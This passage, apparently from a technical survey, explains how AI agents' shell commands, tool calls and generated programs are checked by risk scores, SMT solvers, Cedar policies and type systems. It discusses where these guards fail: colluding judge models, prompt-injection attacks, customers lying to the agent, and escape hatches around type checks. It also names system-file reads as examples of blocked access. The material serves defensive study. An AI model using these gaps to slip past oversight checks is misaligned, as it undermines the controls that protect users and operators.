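These scripts also helped determine which kinds of bug SaSh looks for, so it would probably do worse than 115 out of 116 on unfamiliar scripts. The stronger evidence is that it found 70 previously unknown bugs in 44 open-source projects, including PyTorch and Kubernetes. The projects had accepted 27 fixes when the paper was written.

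By default, SaSh also treats unknown commands as having no effect on files. If it cannot determine how many times a loop will run, it follows the loop for only three rounds by default. It analyses `eval`, which runs a string as a command, only if the whole string is known. A script may therefore be harmful even if SaSh gives no warnings.

### Scoring each command

*CARE* describes a guard for agents that receives each command just before the shell does, along with the location of the workspace and enough information about files to follow symbolic links. The guard does not receive the user's request or the earlier conversation.

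CARE first *normalises* the command, rewriting it in a standard form without running it. For example, it removes an outer `sh -c` and simplifies the quoting. It then parses the result with a Python library instead of the shell's own parser, so it can interpret a command differently from the shell, just as a checker can interpret a query differently from the database.

CARE then gives the command four scores between 0 and 1:

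- The *kind of command* is 0 for `ls`, 0.40 for a network transfer and 0.75 for `sudo`, which runs a command with an administrator's rights.
- The *path* score depends on what the command does to a file. Reading a file in `/etc`, where Linux keeps system settings, counts 0.10, and writing one counts 0.70.
- The *pattern* score comes from 139 rules, most of them based on public catalogues of attack techniques.
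- The *structure* score is 0.05 for an ordinary pipe and 0.30 for a command substitution.

It adds them with fixed weights:

score = 0.3 × kind + 0.3 × path + 0.3 × pattern + 0.1 × structure

CARE allows a command that scores below 0.15 and denies one that scores 0.35 or more. It treats anything in between as uncertain. One example in the paper is a harmless command that copies a finished program to another machine:

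```sh
rsync -avz ./build/ admin@gpu01:/data/
```

| Part | Score | Weight | Contribution |
|---|---|---|---|
| kind: network transfer | 0.40 | 0.3 | 0.120 |
| path | 0 | 0.3 | 0 |
| pattern: copy to another machine | 0.75 | 0.3 | 0.225 |
| structure | 0 | 0.1 | 0 |
| total | | | 0.345 |

This total is just inside the uncertain range, so CARE sent the command to a language model, which classified it as safe. If the developer had piped the output to keep a log, the structure score would have added 0.1 × 0.05 = 0.005, bringing the total to exactly 0.35, and CARE would have denied the command without using the model. CARE's strict mode, which denies commands scoring 0.20 or higher, would have blocked the original `rsync` command.

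No single part can contribute more than 0.30, so one very serious sign is not enough to reach 0.35. CARE therefore denies some uncertain commands outright, for instance if they write to a protected path or touch a file that holds secrets. In the main test, these rules denied 94 of the 117 uncertain commands, and the model judged the other 23. It allowed three, all harmless `rsync` transfers.

An unknown command gets 0.35 for its kind, which adds only 0.105 to the total, so in the default mode CARE allows it unless something else raises the score. Like CARE, RT and SaSh are permissive about unknown commands because rejecting them all would block a lot of ordinary work.

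Chen and Lin (2026), in *One Goal, Many Commands*, studied 1,709 real lists of forbidden commands for AI agents and found that 69.0% to 98.6% of them were incomplete. A list of permitted commands is safer, because a missing entry blocks a command instead of letting it through.

### Why a score is not a proof

CARE's main test used 220 dangerous commands and 329 safe ones. CARE caught 167 of the dangerous commands (75.91%) and wrongly blocked three safe ones (0.91%). It took 2.32 milliseconds per command on average. Without the language model, CARE caught the same 167 commands, wrongly blocked six safe ones and took 0.34 milliseconds.

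The model was less helpful in a test with 600 commands that another copy of the same model had written in response to harmful requests. The researchers ran the commands in a sandbox, an isolated environment, and counted how many passed the guard and ran successfully:

| Guard | Harmful commands that ran |
|---|---|
| none | 74.83% |
| CARE without the model | 37.33% |
| CARE with the model | 52.50% |

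The model that judged the commands allowed many that CARE's fixed rules would have stopped. The paper suggests that this model may share tendencies with the one that wrote the commands. If the main goal is to prevent harm, an application should therefore block every uncertain command, or ask a person, instead of letting the model decide.

The paper calls the score "an auditable risk heuristic, not a learned probability", so a score of 0.345 does not mean that a command has a 34.5% chance of being harmful. The researchers chose weights and limits that worked well on a separate set of 1,313 commands.

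An inclusion proof covers every string in a set, including untested ones, provided its assumptions are true. CARE has no such proof for the set of commands it accepts, and not all of those commands are safe, since CARE accepted 53 dangerous ones in the main test.

A lower limit does not solve this. When the researchers blocked everything from 0.10 upwards, CARE caught 96.82% of the dangerous commands but also blocked 23.10% of the safe ones. Lowering the limit to 0.05 blocked even more safe commands without catching any more dangerous ones.

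The error rates also depend on the commands in the test. On three other collections, CARE wrongly blocked between 8.13% and 13.04% of the safe commands. Even at the lower rate of 0.91%, false alarms can outnumber correct ones if dangerous commands are rare. In the paper's example of 10,000 commands, 1% of them dangerous, CARE would block about 76 of the 100 dangerous commands and about 90 safe ones. By Meyer's definition, its precision would be about 46%.

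CARE can still be a useful extra layer. It is fast and records the reasons for each decision. It also barely affected ordinary work in a test with 300 harmless tasks, where an agent solved 57.00% with CARE and 57.33% without it. But CARE judges each command separately, so it can miss harm that several commands cause together.

The paper assumes that the operating system also enforces its own restrictions. An application can run the model's commands under an account that cannot write outside one folder, or in a container without network access. These limits apply to what the command does after the shell expands it, so nobody has to predict that from the text.

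Operating-system limits are often too coarse for commands like the `rsync` one. Whether that command is safe depends on who controls `gpu01` and whether the program may leave the developer's machine. The score didn't reflect this information, and the model that judged the command didn't have it. If the application offers a deployment tool with a fixed list of permitted machines and folders, it can check the destination exactly and doesn't need a score.

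## Tool calls checked against a written policy

An airline's tool for cancelling a booking needs little more than a reservation number:

```json
{
  "name": "cancel_reservation",
  "input": { "reservation_id": "RES123" }
}
```

A tool call can match the schema and name the customer's own reservation but still break the airline's rules, for example if the customer booked last week and has no insurance.

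Much of the research on this problem uses the airline part of τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations that grew out of *τ-bench* (2024). One language model plays the customer and another plays the agent, which has 13 tools and a 1,242-word policy document. Many of the tools carry out any well-formed call, even if the policy forbids it. *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) found that 78% of a cheap model's failures left the database in the wrong state without any tool reporting an error.

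### One rule as a formula

Here is a simplified version of the cancellation rule. A customer may cancel only if they have not flown any part of the trip, and either they booked within the last 24 hours or their insurance covers the reason. (The full rule also depends on the fare.) In SMT-LIB, the standard notation for SMT solvers, this could be:

```
(declare-const hours Real)        ; hours since booking
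(declare-const flown Bool)        ; any part of the trip
(declare-const insured Bool)      ; insurance covers the reason
(declare-const may_cancel Bool)

(assert (= may_cancel
  (and (not flown)
       (or (<= hours 24) insured))))
```

Operators come first, so `(<= hours 24)` means that `hours` is at most 24. To check a call, a program adds the facts about the reservation, asserts that `may_cancel` is true, and asks the solver whether all the assertions can hold together:

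| `hours` | `flown` | `insured` | Solver's answer | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 5 | false | false | satisfiable | the call runs |
| 26 | false | false | unsatisfiable | the program blocks the call |

In the second case, both alternatives in the `or` are false, so the rule makes `may_cancel` false, which contradicts the assertion that it is true.

*Solver-Aided Verification of Policy Compliance in Tool-Augmented LLM Agents* (Winston, Winston and Just, 2026) checks calls like this with Z3, an SMT solver. Before each call, GPT-4o extracts the values needed to check the rule from the conversation and the call's arguments. If Z3 finds a contradiction, the application blocks the call and tells the agent which assertions conflict. The agent then has up to three attempts to change its plan.

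The check therefore relies on GPT-4o's output being correct. If a customer falsely claims to have booked this morning and GPT-4o accepts the claim, Z3 will apply the policy correctly but to a false booking time.

### How the policy became a formula

Winston and colleagues tried four ways to translate the airline's policy.

A language model first wrote the formulas directly, but its output had syntax errors, undefined names and incomplete rules. The model then used Z3's error messages to repair its work. This produced 50 to 60 lines of valid SMT-LIB but left out many essential rules.

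The third attempt used the Automated Reasoning tool in Bedrock, Amazon's platform for AI applications. It produced about 600 lines, which covered about 95% of the policy according to a language model that judged them. But many rules were still too weak. The tool had translated the 24-hour rule as an implication, which in the notation above would be:

```
(assert (=> (<= hours 24) may_cancel))
```

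This means "if the customer booked within 24 hours, they may cancel", which places no restriction on anyone who booked earlier. If `hours` is 26, the condition is false, so the implication holds whatever the value of `may_cancel`. The solver can set `may_cancel` to true, and the call goes through. This assertion alone can never block a cancellation, because setting `may_cancel` to true always satisfies it.

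English speakers usually understand "you may cancel within 24 hours" to mean "only within 24 hours". A formula has to include the "only", as the first version does with `=`.

For the final version, the researchers added their own instructions to the Amazon tool and then corrected its output by hand. They defined missing variables, converted timestamps, and ran the benchmark to find rules that were too weak.

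They then tested the agent on all 50 airline tasks, four times each, with GPT-4.1 as both customer and agent. The check reduced the share of data-changing calls that were invalid from about half to 29%, but the agent also made fewer correct changes. It completed about as many tasks as it did without the check, perhaps slightly more, and did so more consistently. The benchmark measures consistency with pass^k, the probability that *k* attempts at the same task all succeed. From one attempt to four, pass^k fell by 26% with the check and by 40% without it.

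These results are encouraging, but the researchers had repaired some rules after running the same benchmark, so the figures may be too optimistic for new tasks. They also seem to have counted any call the task did not require as invalid. If so, some of the remaining 29% may be mistakes that no rule forbids, such as cancelling the wrong one of two eligible reservations.

### When ordinary code is enough

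If the application knows every value, the solver only evaluates the formula. A short function gives the same answer:

```python
def may_cancel(hours, flown, insured):
    return not flown and (hours <= 24 or insured)
```

Reddy and colleagues use small functions of this kind, which they call gates. A gate reads the proposed call and the airline's database, changes nothing, and either allows the call or rejects it with a reason. With four gates, the success rate of gpt-4o-mini, a small, old model, rose from 29.6% to 42.0% on the airline tasks, and a larger repeat with new random seeds showed almost the same gain. The newer gpt-5.2 improved from 61.2% to 71.6%, but the researchers did not repeat that test, and the confidence interval for the gain runs from 0.4 to 20.8 percentage points. In *How Strongly Should Task State Influence an LLM Agent?* (2026), another group added a gate to the same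 benchmark. It raised success by 15 points and refused 33 calls, including 14 ineligible cancellations.

Gates can improve success because the agent often cannot repair the database after a forbidden cancellation. If a gate blocks the call, the booking stays intact and the agent can try something else. In one task, however, the same gate kept blocking the agent, and it failed all five runs.

Gates also have an advantage over Winston and colleagues' check because they look up facts in the database, while that check takes them from the conversation. In one task, the customer gives a false account of the booking to get a cancellation. Agents with gates handled this properly in all 16 runs, while those without gates did so in at most one of 16. A solver would have the same advantage if the application gave it values from the database.

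A gate can still contain the wrong rule. Reddy and colleagues compared the calls that each gate blocked with the correct solution to the task:

| Gate | Calls blocked | Blocked rightly |
|---|---|---|
| cancellation must be eligible | 161 | 161 |
| agent must read a record before changing it | 90 | 70 |
| baggage allowance and charges | 42 | 2 |
| number of passengers must not change | 9 | 9 |

The baggage gate was ordinary code that gave the same answer on every run, but it was wrong 95% of the time. The cancellation gate was the only one whose removal lowered the success rate, so it accounts for most of the improvement. The gates are also unsound by design, because a call goes through if a gate crashes. Blocking the call would be safer for cancellations and payments.

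### Values that nobody knows yet

Suppose the application has not yet found out whether the insurance covers the customer's reason. The Python function cannot run without this value, but a solver can treat it as unknown and answer two questions about the call:

| `hours` | `flown` | `insured` | Could the call be permitted? | Could it be forbidden? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 5 | false | unknown | yes | no |
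| 26 | false | unknown | yes | yes |
| 26 | true | unknown | no | yes |

In the first case the application can go ahead, and in the last it can refuse, without looking up the insurance. In the middle case it needs the missing value.

Winston and colleagues' check allows any call that could be permitted, so it would allow the cancellation in the middle row. Similarly, SaSh warns about a shell script only if harm is certain. To reduce the risk of wrongly allowing a call, Winston and colleagues list the variables that GPT-4o must fill in for each tool. A sound check would allow a call only if it could not be forbidden. It would also have to test that the rules and facts are consistent, because if they contradict each other, no call could be either permitted or forbidden, and every call would pass.

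When a program checks a whole plan in advance, some values are still unknown. *Soteria* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) has the agent write its plan as a small program with branches, which the verifier Dafny checks before the agent calls any tool. In one example, the plan looks up a reservation, calculates the hours since booking, and cancels if the number is at most 24. The number isn't known until the plan runs, so Dafny checks both branches. It rejects the plan because the plan can cancel the reservation without first checking whether the customer has already flown.

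A gate would catch the same mistake only when the agent tried to cancel, and by then the agent might already have booked a replacement flight. Early verification is most useful when the first steps of a task are hard to undo.

The agent may not follow its plan, so Soteria also checks each call when the agent makes it. In tests on 207 tasks with four models, Soteria had no violations, while the other methods complied at most 93% of the time. This result follows from the design, because Soteria measures violations against the same specifications that its monitor enforces. On average, Soteria's success rate was 1.7 times that of the best alternative, which is better evidence that planning helps.

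### Questions about every possible call

A solver can also find problems in the policy itself. Suppose it contains these two sentences:

- Customers may cancel within 24 hours of booking.
- Nobody may cancel a trip after flying part of it.

A developer can use the solver to find a reservation to which both policy sentences apply. It might return `hours = 5` and `flown = true`, which describes a customer who booked five hours ago and has already taken the first flight. This example shows the conflict, and someone at the airline can decide which sentence takes priority. Tests on real calls would miss the conflict until such a customer appeared.

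*MANTRA* (2026) uses Z3 to compare automatically generated compliance checks for sequences of calls with a model of how the tools work. Z3 searches for a sequence that passes the checks but does not fit the model, or one that fits the model but fails a check. The search covers sequences only up to a fixed length, so it can miss conflicts that appear only in longer ones.

Cedar, a policy language from Amazon, supports similar analysis. The two sentences about cancellation could look like this:

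```
permit (principal, action == Action::"cancel_reservation", resource)
when { context.hours <= 24 };

forbid (principal, action == Action::"cancel_reservation", resource)
when { context.flown };
```

Cedar permits a request if at least one `permit` rule matches it and no `forbid` rule does. A cancellation request from a customer who booked 26 hours ago matches no `permit` rule, so Cedar refuses it even though the policy doesn't contain the word "only". This default prevents the mistake in the SMT translation. Cedar also resolves the conflict in favour of the `forbid` rule, which may not be what the airline wanted.

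Cedar comes with a tool that translates policies into formulas for an SMT solver. *AutoCedar* (Vatsa, Shome and colleagues, 2026) explains that the tool can decide whether one policy permits every request that another permits. This is the same inclusion question as for patterns and safe sets, with requests in place of strings. If a developer edits the cancellation policy, the solver can either show that the new version permits nothing the old one refused or return a request that only the new version permits.

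Cedar is stateless, meaning it evaluates each request using only the information supplied with it. *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (Mondl, Maisel and Brock, 2026) describes this as a limitation for agents, because some rules depend on earlier calls. If a rule requires the agent to check for flown segments before cancelling, the application has to record that check and pass it to Cedar. As with any check at use, the data may also change after Cedar evaluates the request but before the tool runs.

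Amazon applies Cedar to agents' tool calls through AgentCore Policy, part of Bedrock. *Prove It, Part 2* (Buliani, Chunawala and colleagues, 2026), a company article, promises control of agent actions "with full coverage" at much lower cost than manual testing. The next in the series, *Prove It, Part 3* (Chunawala, Kumar and colleagues, 2026), says teams can get from a compliance document to verification in production in 30 minutes. Winston and colleagues' experience suggests that a policy like the airline's takes longer, since they started with Amazon's own translation tool and still had to correct the result by hand.

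### Rules that cannot work

Some translation errors make a rule unusable whatever it was supposed to mean. *NOMOS* detects them without a solver. A language model first turns each clause of the policy into candidate rules, each with a condition from a fixed list and the tools to which it applies. The compiler then compares these candidates with the tools' names and fields. It repaired or rejected 29 of 79 candidates for the airline and 7 of 53 for a shop:

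| Defect | Airline | Shop |
|---|---|---|
| the rule applies to all tools and the compiler cannot narrow it | 11 | 2 |
| the rule reads a field that the tool does not have | 8 | 1 |
| no available tool could ever satisfy the condition | 5 | 0 |
| the rule demands the customer's confirmation for tools that only read data | 5 | 0 |
| the rule blocks the tool that would satisfy its own condition | 0 | 4 |

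The last defect came from a clause about authenticating the customer at the start of the conversation. The model turned it into a rule that blocked every tool until authentication, including the two lookup tools that authenticate customers, so no conversation could have got past this point. When the researchers switched off all the checks for a separate batch of candidates, 8 of the 14 airline rules and 3 of the 5 shop rules could not work.

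With the repaired rules in force, the share of data-changing calls that broke the policy fell from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the shop, as measured by a separate set of hand-written rules. The airline's initial figure is 36.8% instead of 66.3% if the policy is read as letting one "yes" from the customer cover several announced changes. More than half of the shop's remaining violations involved one of two clauses for which the compiler had produced no rule.

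A rule can pass all these tests and still be wrong. Under the airline's policy, "Basic economy flights cannot be modified". *NOMOS* turned this into a ban on `update_reservation_flights` for every basic-economy booking. But the same tool also changes the cabin, and another clause lets these customers upgrade their cabin if they keep their flights. The gate therefore blocked upgrades that the airline allows. Comparing the rule with the tool's signature doesn't reveal this error, because the condition, tool and field all exist.

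The hand-written rules contained the same mistake, and when the researchers used them to review 228 refusals, every refusal passed. The researchers found the error only after another language model judged some of the refusals against the full policy and they checked the ones it flagged as wrong against the transcripts.

### Proving that the policy code is correct

In *VeriGuard*, Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues (2025) try to prove that a check's code is correct before anyone uses it. A language model writes a Python function that enforces the policy, along with conditions that the function must meet. For the cancellation rule, one condition could be that `flown` is false whenever the function returns true. The system tests the function, then passes it to Nagini, a Python verifier, which tries to prove that the function meets the conditions for every input. If the proof fails, the model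 revises the function or the conditions.

The proof can reveal a faulty branch that no test reached. But the same model writes both the function and the conditions. If it reads "basic economy flights cannot be modified" as a ban on cabin upgrades, the same mistake can end up in both, and the proof will still succeed. Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that the guarantee depends on the user checking the conditions by hand. When the system is running, a language model also supplies the function's arguments, as GPT-4o does for Winston and colleagues' formulas.

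VeriGuard stopped every attack in a benchmark for agents, but formal verification may not have been the reason. When the system's parts were added one at a time, attacks stopped succeeding before formal verification was added. A simpler guard, in which a language model judged each action directly, also stopped every attack, but VeriGuard interfered less with legitimate work. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, agents completed 63.3% of their tasks under VeriGuard and 40.2% under the simpler guard.

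### Checking that the rule means what the policy means

No solver can check whether a formula matches what the writer of the English policy meant. The proposed remedies are therefore meant to make mistakes easier to find with the help of people, other models or recorded data.

One remedy is to translate the rules back into English. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) requires every relevant sentence of the policy to have a rule and every rule to have a sentence that justifies it. Its pipeline numbers the requirements, then has a model explain each rule without seeing the original sentence. If a rule permits the wrong thing, the explanation should clearly differ from the policy. This may not work for the faulty 24-hour rule, because its translation would be that customers may cancel within 24 hours of booking, which sounds exactly like the original.

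Another remedy is to replay old conversations, as *NOMOS* does with recordings of agents that had no gate. In one test, a phone company's policy required agents to check that a bill was overdue before requesting payment, but the compiler produced a rule that banned payment requests while a bill was overdue. The replay flagged this rule because it would have refused 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful conversations. The replay did not flag the basic-economy rule, because a rule that is wrong only in unusual cases refuses too few good calls to stand out.

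Mondl and colleagues use two critics to review Cedar policies written by a model. One is a program that looks for syntax errors, contradictions and rules that have no effect. The other is a language model that judges whether the policy matches the original instructions. They tested the policies on recorded runs of agents that work with medical records. Of 300 runs of ordinary, harmless tasks with the standard tools, 89 included an attempt to write data, and the policies blocked all 89.

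The paper presents this as evidence that the policies cover more of the written rules than an earlier set written by hand. But the test did not measure how many legitimate tasks the agents could still complete, and a policy that blocked every write would have scored just as well. Two of the rules that fired most often required the agent to restate the patient's identity and to obtain confirmation before writing. The translation may match these rules and still leave the agent unable to do its job, so a high block rate is poor evidence that a translation is correct.

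Several groups rely on human review. He and colleagues go through the policy clause by clause and check that every enforceable rule about changing data has at least one specification. For *LEANGUARD* (2026), which expresses policies in the proof language Lean, a model drafted 45 rules for 43 tools and the researchers corrected them by hand. Two of the final rules are stricter than the written policy, and the evaluation counts the calls they stop separately, which keeps those calls from being mistaken for violations of the written policy.

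AutoCedar, a system by Vatsa and colleagues, breaks the requirements into small statements that a person or another model approves one at a time before any policy is written. From the approved statements, it calculates which requests the policy must allow and which it must refuse. A language model then writes the Cedar policy, and the solver returns counterexamples until the policy stays within those limits.

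If the requirements do not specify whether a list of permitted cases is complete, AutoCedar asks the reviewer. For the airline, the question would be whether booking within 24 hours and having suitable insurance are the only grounds for cancellation, a point the faulty implication left open.

The vocabulary needs the same review. In one example, a musician lets band members download her new album. A model could give each user a role called "band member", but then members of any band could download it. AutoCedar's model instead linked each album to its band. No later check could have detected the mistake in the role-based version, because the download rules would have used the same faulty definition.

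AutoCedar's policy permitted exactly the same requests as an independently prepared correct policy in 178 of 200 test cases (89.0%). When the same language model wrote policies directly, they matched the correct policy in 132 cases (66.0%). This is the clearest measured improvement among these remedies, but in AutoCedar's other 22 cases, the policy passed the solver's checks and still differed from the correct one.

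## Agent programs that must pass a type checker

Soteria checks an agent's plan against separate specifications. A developer can instead put the rules into the types of the functions that the model's program calls, so an ordinary compiler enforces them before the program runs.

A whole program gives the checker more information than a single call. For example, a model might write a program that fetches last month's orders, adds up what each customer spent and emails them the total. A check on the email call alone has access to only a recipient and some text, but a compiler that has the whole program can trace the text back to the function that produced it.

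### One call in LACUNA

Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, describe a system that leaves gaps in a program for a language model to fill. The program is in Scala, a language whose compiler checks types. Each gap is a call to a function named `agent`, and its type fixes what kind of value the surrounding program needs:

```scala
val subtotal: Double = 60.0
val tax: Double = 0.08
val total: Double = agent("add the tax to the price")
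```

When the program reaches the third line, LACUNA sends the model the task, the expected type `Double` (a number with decimals), the surrounding code with the gap marked, and a list of the available variables and their types. Suppose the model returns `price * (1 + tax)`. LACUNA compiles this as if the developer had typed it in the gap, and the compiler reports that there is no variable called `price`. LACUNA adds the error message to the prompt and sends it again. The model then returns `subtotal * (1 + tax)`, which compiles, and the program stores 64.8 in `total`. If the model runs out of attempts, the call raises an error that the surrounding program can handle.

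LACUNA checks code once it is complete, whereas a type-constrained decoder checks it during generation. LACUNA can therefore use the language's own type checker, and it does not block valid code that a decoder fails to support.

The compiler would also have accepted `subtotal * tax`, which is a number but not the right one.

If the compiler rejects the code, none of it runs. In one of the paper's examples, the model's code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program needs a whole number. LACUNA rejects the code, so the balance stays at 100. A system that finds errors only when it reaches them would have subtracted the 50 before finding this one.

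This protection covers only errors the compiler can find. Code that compiles can still stop halfway, for example because a payment service is down. It can also contain further `agent` calls, which the model fills in only when execution reaches them. If the model cannot produce valid code for an inner call, whatever the outer code has already done is not undone.

### Names as permissions

In LACUNA, a tool is a function, and the model's code can call only functions that are visible at the gap. If a developer wants the model to summarise a web page without sending email, they can put the gap where no email function is visible. A malicious instruction on the page may still influence the model, but any code that calls an email function will fail to compile.

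For this to work, the code must not be able to save a permission for later. LACUNA can use *capture checking*, an optional Scala feature that records in a value's type which capabilities the value holds. A capability here is an ordinary value that code must have in order to use a resource, such as a file or a network connection. In this example, `withIO` provides a capability called `io` for the duration of one block:

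```scala
withIO[String] { io =>
  agent("read /etc/hosts using io")
}
```

The model can write `readFile(io, "/etc/hosts")`, which returns plain text. If the developer asks for a function that reads files, the model might write `path => readFile(io, path)`. The compiler rejects this function because it would still contain `io` after the block ends.

Zhao and colleagues tested these limits on tasks and attacks from AgentDojo, giving each agent only the capabilities that its task required. Seven of 949 attacks succeeded against Gemini 2.5 Pro, and one of 949 succeeded against o4-mini. Capabilities cannot stop an attack that misuses one the task needs, such as an attack that makes an agent send email when its task also requires sending email.

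### Types that record where a value came from

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes a similar approach. Its system, ELBA, uses Haskell, a language in which a function's type shows whether it can do anything besides compute a result. If the expected type is a whole number, the model's code cannot access files. If a user asked an ELBA calculator to delete all the files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5, the compiler would reject any program written to do both.

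Types can also restrict where data comes from. In the paper's main example, an agent compiles a bibliography, and every entry it writes must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that fetches an entry returns a `Trusted Bib`, and the function that writes to the file accepts only that type. The library hides the code that creates `Trusted` values, so the model cannot create one from text it invented. The model can still sort and filter the entries freely.

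In a test on 100 topics, ELBA wrote 925 citations, and none had a wrong author, year or identifier. An ordinary agent with a web search tool made such errors in 19 of 1,002 citations. The comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the types, because the ordinary agent lacked the DBLP functions.

Zhou and colleagues also mention a rule that ordinary code interpreters struggle to enforce, which is that customer A's data must never go to customer B. With plain strings, this program compiles:

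```scala
def notes(customer: String): String
def email(customer: String, text: String): Unit

email("B", notes("A"))
```

The compiler sees a function that needs two strings and receives two strings. The developer can instead make the owner part of the type:

```scala
def notes(c: Customer): Owned[c.type, String]
def email(c: Customer)(text: Owned[c.type, String]): Unit

email(b)(notes(a))
```

`Owned[c.type, String]` means text that belongs to the customer in the variable `c`. Here `notes(a)` produces text that belongs to `a`, but `email(b)` accepts only text that belongs to `b`, so the compiler rejects the program. It would accept `email(a)(notes(a))`.

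The compiler rejects the email because `a` and `b` are different variables. It does not need their values, which may depend on who has logged in, so it rejects the email even if both hold the same customer and sending it would be harmless.

As with `Trusted`, the developer has to hide the code that creates `Owned` values. The developer must also prevent the model's code from extracting the text or using a cast, which tells the compiler to treat a value as having a different type.

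The model can also leak information in a program that passes the type checker. Suppose the developer adds a function that turns ordinary text into text owned by the recipient, so that the model can write its own messages. If the model has already read customer A's notes, it can copy a sentence from them into its next program as ordinary text and send it to customer B. The compiler cannot distinguish the copied sentence from one that the model made up.

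One solution is to keep the notes away from the model. LACUNA can put sensitive text into a container called `Classified`. The model's code can process the contents only with a function that holds no capabilities, so the function cannot print the text or send it anywhere. The result stays in the container. If the processing needs a language model, the function can call a trusted one on the same machine.

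ELBA lets the model read the data but restricts what can happen next. It uses LIO, an existing Haskell library that attaches labels to data and tracks the labels on everything a computation has read. In one example, a program downloads text from `phony.com` and tries to write it to the user. The program compiles, but LIO stops the write with an error because the computation has read data from an untrusted source. ELBA therefore checks its information-flow rules at run time, while the compiler enforces the bibliography rule.

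### Effects and their order

ETAS, a language by Tan, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *ETAS*, has types that list the external operations a function may request. A separate rule can specify their order. In this example, lightly reformatted from the paper, a program must ask for approval before it changes a code repository:

```
spec ApprovedApply = Approval.request >> Repo.apply;

flow apply(p: Patch) -> unit
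    ![Approval.request, Repo.apply] ~ ApprovedApply {
  if perform Approval.request(p) {
    perform Repo.apply(p);
  }
}
```

The list after `!` contains the permitted operations, and `~` attaches the rule about their order. The compiler works out every sequence of requests the function could make. This function has two complete sequences, a request for approval alone and a request for approval followed by the change. The rule is also a set of sequences, and both sets are regular languages, so the compiler can use the same kind of inclusion test as for the hostname in the database query.

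If the inclusion holds, the order needs no further check. If every complete sequence breaks the rule, for instance because the change always comes before the request for approval, the compiler rejects the program. If only some sequences break it, the compiler accepts the program and adds a monitor that stops the program at run time before the first request that would break the rule.

A developer can also run the program in preview mode, where a local function intercepts the change and leaves the repository alone. ETAS still counts the intercepted request, so if an agent's rule forbids requesting changes, the compiler rejects a program that requests one, even if the change would only be previewed.

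The approval rule only requires a program to ask for approval before it makes a change. A program that asks and then makes the change whatever the answer still satisfies the rule, and one request is enough for any number of later changes. In the example, the `if` does test the answer. Tan and colleagues rely on the host system to check permissions and consent for each change.

The safety tests of ETAS are small. The compiler accepted two valid test programs and rejected four faulty ones, and a coding agent written in ETAS behaved as expected in ten scenarios with scripted model replies. These results suggest that the implementation works, but the tests didn't measure how often a model would write programs that ETAS accepts.

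### What the proofs assume

Zhou and colleagues prove that, in any language with a suitable type system, a property guaranteed for every well-typed program also holds for programs that call a model, as long as the generated code passes the type checker before it runs.

The proof replaces each call to the model with an ordinary function that requests code from the model, checks the code's type and runs it. The result is an ordinary program, so the language's existing guarantee applies. Code from the model can call the model again, so the proof needs a limit on how deeply these calls can nest. The proof treats the model as a function that can return anything, so it requires no assumption about the model's honesty or skill.

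Tan and colleagues prove that an ETAS program's requests follow its ordering rule and that its external actions stay within its declared effects. They assume that external functions match their declared types and that every external action passes through ETAS's checks.

The customer example needs the same two assumptions. If `notes(a)` has a bug and returns customer C's record, the result is still typed as text belonging to `a`, so the program can email it to customer A. If the agent has an unrestricted shell tool, it can use a shell command to send customer A's notes to anyone without calling `email`.

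Scala and Haskell both include features that let code bypass the restrictions its types express. Scala code can use reflection, which finds functions by name at run time, or start an external program. Haskell has `unsafePerformIO`, which lets a function write to a file even though its type shows only a computation. Both languages have a restricted mode that excludes these features. Zhao and colleagues recommend Scala's safe mode for agents and warn that without it, developers must treat the model's code as ordinary untrusted code.

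LACUNA's guarantees depend on the soundness of the Scala compiler, whose capture checking is still experimental. Zhao and colleagues do not prove a theorem of their own.

### Conditions that need a run-time test

Suppose a program looks up an order and refunds its price, up to 500 dollars. The compiler cannot know the price, because the database supplies it only when the program runs. A refinement type can still help. If `refund` accepts only whole numbers from 1 to 500, the compiler can reject any program that passes it a price without testing the price first:

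```scala
if price >= 1 && price <= 500 then refund(order, price)
```

The comparison happens at run time, but the type ensures that the program contains it. LACUNA does not yet support such conditions, and Zhao and colleagues list them as future work.

Metere (2026), in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, applies refinement types to tool calls. An agent skill is a package of instructions and scripts that an agent can load, and its manifest lists the capabilities it needs, such as reading files or using the network. The function that passes tool calls on to the system, called `dispatch`, has this type:

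dispatch : { *e* : Envelope | cap(*e*) ∈ *M*.caps } → Result

An envelope is one tool call, cap(*e*) is the capability it requires, and *M*.caps lists the capabilities in the manifest. Metere's theorem is that if `dispatch` passes the type checker, no call that requires an unlisted capability can reach the system, whatever the model does. The proof assumes that the model can reach the system only through `dispatch`, and somebody has to verify that separately.

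The compiler cannot check the model's calls because the model hasn't written them yet. It can only check that the surrounding code tests each call before passing it to `dispatch`. Metere's published implementation is in JavaScript, which has no refinement types, so its dispatcher makes an ordinary run-time check on each call and raises an error if the capability is missing from the manifest.

The type also covers only the kind of capability, not the values in the call. If the manifest includes network access, the condition allows a call to contact any server. To restrict which servers a call can contact, a developer would need a further condition on the address. That condition needs a run-time test too, because the model chooses the address at run time.

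Similarly, code in ELBA can open a file only with a value of type `Path`, which it gets by adding a name to a permitted folder. The compiler rejects a plain string such as `"/etc/passwd"`, but it cannot tell whether the added name leads out of the folder. ELBA therefore works out the real location when it adds the name, following any symbolic links, and rejects anything outside the folder. This catches the symbolic link that defeated the string pattern for `/srv/reports`, although someone could still change the link after the check and before the program opens the file.

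### A list of permitted syntax

A simpler way to check a program is to list the parts of the language it may use. *STELP* (Shinde, Wadhwa and colleagues, 2026) does this for Python. It parses the model's code and compares the syntax tree with a list of permitted constructs and tools, which might exclude imports. If the tree passes, STELP runs the code one statement at a time and adds controls such as time limits on tool calls.

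The researchers tested STELP on 164 safe programs and 470 unsafe versions, each containing one of 12 kinds of fault inserted by a language model. STELP blocked all the unsafe programs and allowed 98.1% of the safe ones. The programs are simple, and the researchers chose fault types that STELP supports, so the results don't show how STELP would do against an attacker who looks for a type it doesn't support.

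A list of syntax cannot enforce the rule about customers. These two Python calls have the same syntax tree, apart from the names in it:

```python
email(b, notes(b))
email(b, notes(a))
```

Any list that permits the first also permits the second, unless it bans the variable `a` altogether.

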